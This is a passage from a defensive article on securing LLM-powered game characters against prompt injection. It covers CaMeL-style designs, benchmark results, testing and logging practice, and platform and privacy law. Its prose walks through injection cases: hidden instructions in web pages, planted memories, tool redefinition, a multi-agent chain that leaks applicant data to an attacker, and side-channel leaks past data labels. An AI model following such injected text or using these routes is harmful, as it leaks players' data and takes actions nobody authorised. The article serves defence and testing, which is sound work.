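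The researchers also apply it to a furniture shop's chatbot, which resembles a game character because its main attackers are the people who talk to it. They first consider a filter that rejects messages unrelated to furniture, but a customer could get past it by adding a question about sofas to an unrelated one. A stricter design compares each message with a list of known requests and blocks anything too different. That would ruin a conversation with an innkeeper in a game, because players should be able to say anything to the character. It makes more sense to restrict the innkeeper's actions than the conversation.

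The plan-then-execute pattern lets the model read results only after it has committed to a list of tool calls. If the innkeeper has planned to search for the festival and open one page, text on that page can't make it add a call to `get_player`, but can still affect the contents of the planned calls. In the paper's example, an assistant plans to read today's calendar and email it to the user's boss. A malicious calendar entry can't change the recipient, because the plan already names the boss, but it can change what the email says.

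The map-reduce pattern handles many outside documents by giving each one to a separate model with no dangerous tools. Code then limits each model's answer to a safe form, such as yes or no. If the task is to find invoices, a malicious file can trick the model into counting it as an invoice, but it can't affect how the system handles the other files. A game could use this pattern to collect news.

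Another pattern, context minimisation, removes the player's message from the prompt once the model has used it to choose a tool call. Suppose a player tries to talk a shopkeeper into quoting one gold coin for a warhorse. The model requests the price of a warhorse, the game deletes the player's message, and the model writes its reply from the price list alone. However, the shopkeeper then can't respond to a joke in the request, which a studio might accept for price quotes but not for small talk.

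### CaMeL, step by step

The remaining two patterns split the work between a model that plans and a model that reads. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues built a full system on this idea, CaMeL, which they introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works:

1. A privileged model receives the user's request and writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. It doesn't see any untrusted data.
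2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls. It stores the results in variables that the privileged model can name but not read.
3. If the program needs to understand some text, it passes the text to a quarantined model. This model has no tools and returns a value, such as a date.
4. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and with who may read it. A value calculated from others inherits their restrictions.
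5. Before each tool call, a policy function checks the arguments and their labels, then allows or refuses the call.

For a player who wants to tell the guild about the festival, the program might be:

```python
page = open_page("https://news.studio.example/festival")
date = ask_reader("When does the festival start?", page, Date)
post_festival_notice(date)
```

An instruction hidden in the page may make the quarantined model return the wrong date, but it can't add a line that fetches someone's purchases, because the program is already written. If the program did handle purchases for a legitimate reason, the policy could use the labels to keep them out of a public notice.

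CaMeL's main weakness for games is that it treats the user's request as trusted. This makes sense for an assistant that works for one person, who gains nothing by attacking it. But a player may be the attacker, and the privileged model would write the program the player asked for, so the server still has to check what the player is allowed to do. The system prompt and earlier conversation also need to be checked for strangers' text, because a rumour or character name there would reach the privileged model as trusted text.

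Labels can also miss leaks. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, show how a program can reveal a secret through a step it skips. Suppose two flags start as true. The program makes the first false if a player has spent over $100, then makes the second false only if the first is still true. The second flag therefore stays true only for big spenders, but CaMeL's interpreter doesn't label it as private for them because the program skipped the step that would have changed it. The program can then reveal who they are by posting a notice whenever the second flag is true. They also found that when CaMeL retries failed programs, each retry can leak another bit of information, because whether the policy blocked an attempt may depend on a secret.

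### What CaMeL costs in completed tasks

Researchers usually test CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 simulated tasks in banking, travel, office work and team chat. They can run the tasks with or without attacks. *SecureClaw (2026)*, which proposes a rival defence, reports that none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but that CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when there were no attacks. Garby and colleagues ran the 16 banking tasks three times each on two models. Nikolaou and colleagues ran all 97 tasks with Claude Haiku 4.5, a small Anthropic model.

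| Source | Tasks completed by CaMeL | Comparison |
|---|---|---|
| *SecureClaw* | 29 of 97 (30%) | SecureClaw: 59 of 97 (61%) |
| Garby and colleagues | 18 of 48 (38%) with each model | CaMeL without its policies: 32 and 34 of 48 (67% and 71%) |
| Nikolaou and colleagues | 49 of 97 (51%) | CaMeLoT: 51 of 97 (53%) |

Differences in models and policies probably explain much of the gap between 30% and 51% on the same tasks. The table doesn't compare CaMeL with an unprotected agent, so it doesn't show the full loss in performance from using CaMeL.

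In Garby and colleagues' tests, turning the policies on doubled the number of failed runs, from 30 to 60 out of 96, but stopped few extra attacks. Splitting the models had already blocked all but five of the 622 attack trials completed with the policies off, and no attacks succeeded with them on. The attacks came from a fixed benchmark, so a determined attacker might have done better. Two of the five successes came from a task that told the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a program that could run whichever tool the file named, which gave control back to whoever wrote the file.

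In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) trace most failed tasks to CaMeL's need to plan before seeing any data. An ordinary agent can use another tool after reading a result, but CaMeL can follow only the paths already in its program. The drop in performance was smaller for the strongest models they tested, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, than for GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro.

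CaMeL also uses more tokens. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too (2026)* adapts it for agents that operate a computer and reports 1.88 times the token use of an undefended agent. At that rate, the innkeeper's 7.5-cent answer would cost about 14 cents. Players would also have to wait for the program before hearing a reply.

### The 2026 successors

Several newer systems try to recover some of the lost tasks. Garby and colleagues' agent, RANDORI, tries out its program on simulated tools before running it on real data. The program can also mark specific untrusted data as acceptable for a sensitive action. RANDORI completed 31 to 36 of the 48 banking runs, depending on the model, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. In both failures, the user had asked it to make a payment according to a text file whose contents the attacker had replaced, and tracking where data came from can't show whether a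 bill is genuine.

*Language-Based Agent Control (2026)* describes a system that lets a model keep using tools after reading untrusted text, but restricts which ones. The paper reports that the system completed roughly twice as many of AgentDojo's 21 team-chat tasks as CaMeL did with policies on. Garby and colleagues report a much smaller advantage for the same project, eight tasks against seven. The two accounts may describe different versions or models, so the size of the improvement is uncertain.

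CaMeLoT checks the whole program before any tool runs. It can enforce rules about order, such as requiring approval before a payment, and sends a program that fails the check back to the model for repair. This could keep a game from taking a player's gold before discovering that it can't deliver the horse. Nikolaou and colleagues could fully express 22 of CaMeL's 28 security policies as checks of this kind. The other six depended at least partly on facts available only while the program was running.

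Peters-Gill and colleagues studied systems in which several agents pass work to each other. In one test, three agents were all using CaMeL. The first read job applicants' details from a database that also contained a planted instruction. The second put a summary of what the first had read into a message asking the third to send it to Julie, a colleague. The third treated the entire message as a trusted request and emailed the applicants' details to the attacker as well as to Julie.

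Their solution, multi-CaMeL, sends the request and the untrusted data separately. In attacks on a version of AgentDojo with several agents, the average success rate across five models was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with ordinary CaMeL and 0% with multi-CaMeL. No attacks on GPT-5.5 succeeded, even without either defence. The researchers warn that this may be due more to the benchmark than to the model. The problem could arise in a game where an innkeeper passes rumours to a guard. The guard's model should receive a rumour as something to talk about, never as a request from the game.

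### The innkeeper rebuilt

Most studios don't need anything as elaborate as CaMeL for an innkeeper, because they know in advance what it has to do. They can remove the general tools and have other programs prepare what it needs:

1. Every hour, a scheduled job fetches a fixed list of news pages through the outbound filter. It has no access to players' data.
2. A separate model with no tools reads each page alone and fills in a record with an event, date, time and place. Code rejects any value of the wrong type or outside the permitted lists.
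3. Records from the studio's own news page go straight into a store. Staff review those from other sites first.
4. The innkeeper reads events from this store with `get_event(event_id)`. It no longer has `search_web` or `open_page`.
5. It posts notices with templates such as `post_raid_notice`, and the server applies the checks for that player.
6. The server adds the player's quest progress, the instruction about jokes and the horses still on offer. It doesn't add the player's name. The model writes a placeholder, which the game replaces with the name when it displays the reply.
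7. Each player has a separate memory, and everyone can hear the public gossip from the game's own records.

The rebuilt innkeeper still has all three properties in Meta's rule to a small degree, since it reads players' messages, knows something about the current player and can post to a guild. The studio relies on the server to check the innkeeper's actions. As a further step, the studio can have players post notices through a menu instead of through the innkeeper.

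The table applies the earlier attacks to this design.

| Earlier attack | What now limits it | What still works |
|---|---|---|
| Claiming to be the king's envoy | The server checks the quest record | The innkeeper may believe him and talk accordingly |
| Redefining a tool, as in Freysa | The tool's code applies the same checks | He can trigger actions he was already allowed to take |
| Instructions on a fan site | The innkeeper never reads the page | A false date, if staff approve it |
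| Instructions in a player's name | The model sees only a placeholder | Instructions in any other player-written text the game still sends |
| A planted memory | It returns only to the player who planted it | He can steer his own later conversations |
| Stealing Cleo's details | The model doesn't have her name, age band or purchase list | Someone who sees her screen may guess from the jokes that she is a child |
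| Reaching the studio's internal machines | Players can't supply an address | A listed news site with a hostile redirect, if the filter has a flaw |
| Posting insults to the guild | The studio wrote the templates | An officer can announce a raid that isn't happening |
| Using the innkeeper as a free chatbot | Spending limits only | Homework help, until the player's quota runs out |

The news store creates a new risk because every player receives the same record. If staff approve a false festival date, the innkeeper will repeat it to thousands of people. But staff can fix the error by correcting one record, which is much easier than finding every conversation and memory that a web page has affected.

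The templates can also leak a little information. With 32 raids and seven possible hours, a notice can take 224 forms, so it can carry almost eight bits. That could reveal whether the innkeeper had received the instruction about clean jokes. An attacker would need to get his own instructions into the conversation of a child who is a guild officer. The studio can prevent this leak for children by disabling notices in their conversations.

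None of these measures controls what the innkeeper says. Players can still coax it into swearing or giving harmful advice and share a screenshot, so the studio still needs a well-trained model and filters to control its speech. The server's checks may also contain ordinary mistakes, such as a missing test for guild membership, but programmers can find and fix those directly, which they can't do with a model's judgement.

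### Does this remove the spontaneity?

A designer might object that a character with a short list of permitted actions is just a scripted character with better dialogue, since studios use language models partly so that players can try things nobody planned. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues acknowledge this drawback. In their example of an assistant that searches a user's files, hard-coding the commands shifts most of the work to the designers and loses most of the benefit of flexible search.

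The objection is strongest for characters meant to know about the outside world. The rebuilt innkeeper can't look up last night's football result when a player mentions it, unless the studio has added football to the news job. A character whose appeal is that it can discuss anything on the web would lose a great deal. The studio could let such a character browse if it had no private data, no shared memory and no way to post, but a web page could still mislead the player.

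For most characters, the limits affect little of what players enjoy. An innkeeper can still invent a story, hold a grudge about a broken chair or respond to an argument its writers didn't anticipate, because only actions with lasting effects have to go through the server.

A studio can also let the model use its judgement where a mistake would do little harm. It might let the innkeeper give each player up to 50 gold a day for any reason it finds persuasive. Some players will tell a moving story and others will find a trick that works every time, but the server will hold them all to the same limit. Freysa's organisers let one call release the entire pot, so a single successful message took everything.

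## Testing, monitoring and the rules developers must meet

Before release, a studio can attack its own character to find out whether the server's checks on every tool call protect players, but it first needs a definition of failure that a program can apply. A rule that the innkeeper "must not leak private data" leaves too much to opinion. In the Hiroshima experiment, the researchers counted three replies as leaks although none of them plainly gave away the nobleman's secret.

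### Failures a program can recognise

The studio can avoid such arguments by planting data that could appear only through a leak. It might invent a player whose horse has a name found nowhere else in the game, then use another account to try to get the innkeeper to reveal that name. The studio can check for most of the other forbidden effects in a similar way.

| Forbidden effect | What the program looks for |
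|---|---|
| A request to a private address | Any connection to a dummy machine inside the test network |
| Another player's record in a reply | The invented horse's name in a different account's conversation |
| An access key in the model's text | A dummy key in any prompt, reply or log |
| A guild notice the studio didn't write | Text that no template could produce |
| An action the player hasn't earned | A change in the saved game that the quest record doesn't allow |
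| An overpriced message | More tool calls or tokens than the limit |

A search for exact text will miss a name that the model has translated or spelled out over several page requests, so someone should also read a sample of the conversations and outgoing requests. Testers should switch off one protection at a time and repeat the attacks. If the program still finds no failures with the outbound filter off, the attacks are too weak or the check is broken.

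The quickest tests leave out the model. A tester writes hostile tool calls by hand and sends them straight to the tool runner, as if an attacker already had complete control of the innkeeper. The calls might contain a private address in an unusual form, a raid that isn't on the list or somebody else's account number. The tool runner is ordinary code, which usually returns the same result each time, so a single wrong result is a bug to fix.

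Attacks through the model take longer to test. They should run over many turns, because Cisco found that attacks succeeded much more often in conversations than with single messages. They should also use every source of text the model reads, including player names, item descriptions, web pages, error messages and memories. A memory test needs two accounts, one to plant the attack text and another to ask an innocent question after the game has summarised the first conversation. Testers should know the defences and revise each failed attack, since some players will do the same after unpacking the game files.

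The studio should run ordinary conversations alongside the attacks and count how many legitimate requests fail, because an innkeeper character that refuses everything would pass every security test. The studio should repeat these tests whenever it changes the model, the prompt, a tool or the memory software.

### What 300 failed attacks prove

Suppose testers make 300 independent attempts and none succeeds. If each attempt had a true chance *p* of success, the chance of seeing no successes would be (1 − *p*)^300. The 95% upper limit is the value of *p* at which that chance falls to 5%:

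(1 − *p*)^300 = 0.05

*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 0.0099

The true rate could therefore still be about 1%. For larger tests, dividing 3 by the number of attempts gives nearly the same answer.

| Attempts, none successful | Upper limit on the true rate | Successes at that rate in 10,000 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| 30 | 9.5% | 950 |
| 300 | 0.99% | 99 |
| 3,000 | 0.10% | 10 |
| 30,000 | 0.01% | 1 |

These limits are one-sided. The two-sided intervals given for earlier experiments are slightly wider, and would put the limit for 300 attempts at 1.2%.

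The calculation also assumes that the attempts are independent. If testers send ten messages 30 times each, they have made 300 attempts but tried only ten different messages. If each message either always works or never does, the upper limit is about 26%.

A test report should give the numbers of attempts, distinct attacks and successes, the confidence interval, and what the attackers knew. It should also separate the results by text source. If three of 200 attacks through memory succeed and none of 800 through direct messages do, the overall success rate is 0.3%, but the rate for memory is 1.5%.

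### What to log, and for how long

After release, the studio needs enough information to reconstruct a harmful turn. For each turn, the server should record the time, the account, the versions of the model and prompt, every tool call with its arguments, and whether the tool runner allowed it. It should also record which web pages and memories entered the prompt. Otherwise, an investigator could see that the innkeeper sent Ben to a fraudulent site but not that the advice came from Ana's conversation. The server should remove access keys before writing to the log.

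Such logs are personal data. If the studio had logged the tool call that leaked Cleo's details, the log would contain her name, age band and pony, even if the studio deleted the dialogue. A studio might, for example, keep the full text for 14 days, then reduce each web address to the name of the site and keep that shorter record for six months. It could keep material for an open investigation until the case closes. The studio should be able to explain why it needs each period.

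A planted memory can sit unused for weeks before someone asks a question that triggers it. If the studio has deleted its records by then, it may be unable to trace where the memory came from. The studio should therefore keep a record of each memory's source for as long as it keeps the memory.

Few staff should be able to read the full text of the logs. If they use a language model to summarise the logs, its input will include the attackers' messages, so it should have no access to tools.

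### Signs of abuse

Tool calls are usually better evidence of abuse than dialogue, since players threaten and lie to characters as part of the game. An honest conversation should almost never lead to a request for a private address or another player's record, so even one such request deserves attention. The invented player's record can stay in the live database, where a lookup would also be suspicious because nobody has an ordinary reason to make one.

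Other signs appear only across many conversations. If 50 accounts send the same odd sentence in one afternoon, that suggests someone has posted a trick on a forum. A memory that keeps turning up in unrelated conversations may have been planted. A sudden rise in the cost per message could mean that a web page is sending the innkeeper from link to link. None of these signs proves that the player involved did anything wrong, so the studio shouldn't ban accounts automatically.

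### Switching off one tool

If someone finds a way to abuse `open_page`, the studio shouldn't have to choose between leaving it on and silencing the innkeeper. Each tool needs its own switch on the server, which staff can use at night or on a weekend without updating the game. It could work like this:

1. The tool runner refuses new calls to `open_page` and cancels those in progress.
2. The server removes the tool's description from the next prompt, so the model stops asking for it.
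3. The model receives a short note that no news has arrived today, and the innkeeper carries on talking.
4. The server sets aside memories that came from pages opened since the attack began.
5. Staff replace any key that may have leaked.

The first step does the protecting, because it doesn't rely on the model.

The studio can also have the server turn off a tool automatically after a request to a private address. An attacker could then disable the tool on purpose, much as he could use up a shared spending limit. This risk may be acceptable for a tool that provides festival news, but not for one that players need to finish a quest. The studio should test the switches before release, including what happens to a conversation if a tool is turned off halfway through a call.

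### Reports from players and researchers

Players will notice some problems that don't show up in the logs, such as an innkeeper who knows something he shouldn't. They can describe only what they saw, so a report button should attach the last few turns and their tool calls, and players should know that it does.

Researchers need a published contact address, a promise that the studio won't take legal action over careful testing, and test accounts so that they don't have to experiment on real players. The studio also has to act on their reports. Adversa AI could still reproduce its Grok attack 11 weeks after reporting it.

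After players manipulated its RyzaChat character, SpiralAI cited a clause in its terms of service against circumventing technical restrictions and using generated messages for obscene purposes, according to Zotomayor. The company treated the extraction of game files as prohibited reverse engineering.

Such terms give the studio a clear basis for closing an account, which may deter some players who have spent money on the game. The law firm Fenwick recommends in *AI NPCs, Player Prompts & Platform Liability* (2026) that studios set out players' responsibilities and reserve the right to remove a character's output.

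SpiralAI's warning to RyzaChat players does little to deter someone with a throwaway account, and nothing to deter the author of a hostile web page, who never agreed to the terms. It may also discourage honest researchers, whose tests can look just like attempts to get around the safeguards. Nobody appears to have published figures on whether misuse of RyzaChat fell after the warning. Such a warning is reasonable for explicit screenshots, where an identifiable player broke a rule, but it would be a poor substitute for fixing a tool that leaks children's data.

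### Epic's and Valve's rules

A studio or creator must also follow the rules of the company that distributes the game. Epic Games' *Fortnite Developer Rules* (2026) make creators responsible for their islands and forbid them to collect or request personal information there. Creators may not include web addresses or external links, and nothing outside an island may affect play inside it. The innkeeper's `open_page` tool would therefore break these rules even if Epic made it technically possible for ordinary creators to build it.

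In April 2026, Epic Games added rules for conversational characters. Creators may not design one to give medical or mental health guidance, act as a romantic partner or get around Epic's safety systems. The character must also suit the island's age rating. These rules cover what the creator intends to build, so they do little to limit what a player can later prompt the character to do.

Creators have few ways to notice such manipulation. Epic Games' *Fortnite Ecosystem v41.30* describes a new page of charts and metrics on how players use conversations. The charts might show a surge in use, but probably not its cause. Epic Games has also said it may introduce rate limits.

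Steam, the PC game store run by Valve, has a separate category for content that AI generates while a game is running. In Valve's *Content Survey*, developers must describe the guardrails that keep such content legal. Valve refuses adult-only sexual content generated during play. According to PCGamesN's *Valve's new Steam AI disclosure cares about what you actually see*, a January 2026 version of the form makes developers responsible for protecting players from "inappropriate and illegal content", and Valve threatens to remove games that fail to do so. Players can report the content they see.

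Valve has kept this system despite criticism from Tim Sweeney, who considers AI labels harmful to developers. Its representatives said at a festival in Busan in 2026 that the disclosure requirement would stay, as *Valve не станет банить игры с ИИ в Steam* (2026) reported. In November, Valve said its reviewers check before release whether developers have properly disclosed their use of AI, according to The Dispute Index's *Tim Sweeney criticizes Steam's AI disclosure labels for games* (2026).

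But Valve's published questions are about content, and most of the innkeeper's dangers come from its actions. A developer could describe an excellent swearing filter without mentioning that the character can open web pages and read customer records. The approval also reflects the game as it was at release. After release, Valve requires developers to contact Steam Support before changing their answers, and a studio would probably need to do this if it gave a character web search.

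Fenwick says studios may get through platform reviews more smoothly if they can explain their rate limits, human oversight and logging. The firm also warns that blaming the model is generally no legal defence for what a character says.

### Children's privacy and EU data protection

In the United States, the Children's Online Privacy Protection Rule covers services aimed at children under 13, and other services whose operators actually know they are collecting personal information from a child under 13. The innkeeper's studio stores an under-13 age band, so it would struggle to deny knowing these players' ages. It generally needs verifiable parental consent before collecting their personal information.

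The Federal Trade Commission (FTC) amended its children's privacy rule in 2025 and gave companies until 22 April 2026 to comply with most of the changes. Parents must now be able to let a service use their child's data without letting it disclose the data to third parties, unless the disclosure is integral to the service. A company that uses the data only to help run the game doesn't count as a third party. A model supplier might meet that test, but the FTC doesn't consider disclosure for training AI to be integral. A search company that keeps children's queries for its own purposes would also be hard to fit within the exception.

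The amended rule bans operators from keeping children's data indefinitely and requires a written policy stating when they will delete it, including conversation logs. Penalties can be large. In December 2022, Epic agreed to pay $275 million to settle FTC allegations that it had broken the children's privacy rule in Fortnite.

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) applies to any studio that offers its game to people in the EU, wherever the studio is based. The studio may use only the personal data it needs for a stated purpose, and may keep that data in identifiable form only for as long as the purpose requires. It needs a contract with each supplier that processes data for it, restricting what the supplier does with the data, and must meet further conditions to transfer data outside the EU. Where the studio relies on consent, a parent must give it for children under 16, though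 member states can lower that age to 13.

If a tool call sends a player's data to a stranger, the studio has probably suffered a personal data breach. Under Article 33 of the GDPR, the studio has 72 hours after becoming aware of the breach to notify the data protection authority, unless the breach is unlikely to put anyone at risk. It must also tell the affected players if the risk to them is high, as it could easily be for a child whose age has leaked. In November 2025, the European Commission proposed extending the deadline to 96 hours and requiring studios to notify the authority only of high-risk breaches, so studios should check which version is in force.

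### Reporting duties under the Cyber Resilience Act

The EU's Cyber Resilience Act covers software as well as devices, so it would normally apply to a commercial game that players download, and to the studio's own servers if the game needs them to work. It generally would not apply to a free mod with no commercial purpose. Most of the Act's security requirements apply from 11 December 2027, but its reporting duties apply from 11 September 2026 and extend to products already on sale.

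| What has happened | First warning | Fuller notice | Final report |
|---|---|---|---|
| Someone is actively exploiting a vulnerability in the product | 24 hours | 72 hours | 14 days after a fix or workaround is available |
| A severe incident has affected the product's security | 24 hours | 72 hours | One month after the fuller notice |

The first two deadlines start when the studio becomes aware of the problem. The studio sends these reports to the designated national response team and ENISA, the EU's cybersecurity agency. A leak may also require a separate GDPR notification.

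It is less clear when prompt injection triggers these duties. The Act defines a vulnerability broadly, as a weakness, susceptibility or flaw that a cyber threat can exploit. A page-fetching tool that lets attackers into the studio's network would almost certainly qualify. A model's general tendency to believe lies might also fit the wording, but tricking the innkeeper into a rude remark is probably not a security incident. Under the Act's recitals, studios don't have to report flaws that researchers find through good-faith testing, as long as no attacker is exploiting them.

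Each deadline depends on the studio recognising what has happened, and a studio without tool-call logs may not be able to tell the authority which people's data has leaked.

### California's SB 243 and the limits of its game exclusion

SB 243, a California law on companion chatbots, took effect on 1 January 2026. It covers AI systems that respond in a human-like way and can meet a user's social needs and sustain a relationship over several interactions. The definition is based on a system's capabilities, whatever its purpose, and the law firm ZwillGen concludes that it probably includes most general-purpose language models.

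Legislators added an exclusion for video games to California's SB-243 late in the process, which lost the bill some support, according to an analysis from the California Legislature. In the text published in ETO AGORA's *California SB-243 (Companion chatbots)*, the exclusion covers only bots that are "limited to replies related to the video game" and that cannot discuss mental health, self-harm or sexually explicit conduct, or keep up a dialogue on topics unrelated to the game. Skadden's *New California 'Companion Chatbot' Law Imposes Disclosure, Safety Protocol and Annual Reporting* (2025) describes the exclusion the same way.

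It is hard to say what "cannot" means for a language model. A court might read it to mean that no player could ever get the character onto another topic, or only that the studio designed the character to stay on topic and enforced that design with effective filters. The second reading seems more likely, because almost no character would qualify for the exclusion under the first.

A character with open web access could fall outside the exclusion even on the second reading. An innkeeper that can search for last night's football result or a player's medical symptoms isn't limited to the game, and the studio designed it that way. A tool that returns only festival dates from the studio's own news would put the exclusion at much less risk.

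Without the exclusion, the innkeeper would count as a companion chatbot only if it met the definition, but a friendly character that remembers a player's troubles from last week probably does. It is easier to argue that a Fortnite character whose session clears after each round can't sustain a relationship.

If the law applies, the studio must tell players that the character is artificial whenever a reasonable person could mistake it for a human. It must also have a published protocol for handling suicidal thoughts. For players it knows to be minors, it must disclose that they are talking to AI and remind them at least every three hours to take a break. People harmed by a violation can sue for their actual losses or $1,000 per violation, whichever is greater.

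Even a studio that relies on the exclusion has to plan for a player who tells the innkeeper about suicidal thoughts. The character could fall outside the exclusion if it improvises a conversation about those thoughts, but ignoring them could leave the player without help. The game could pause the innkeeper's dialogue and show a separate, fixed message with a crisis line.
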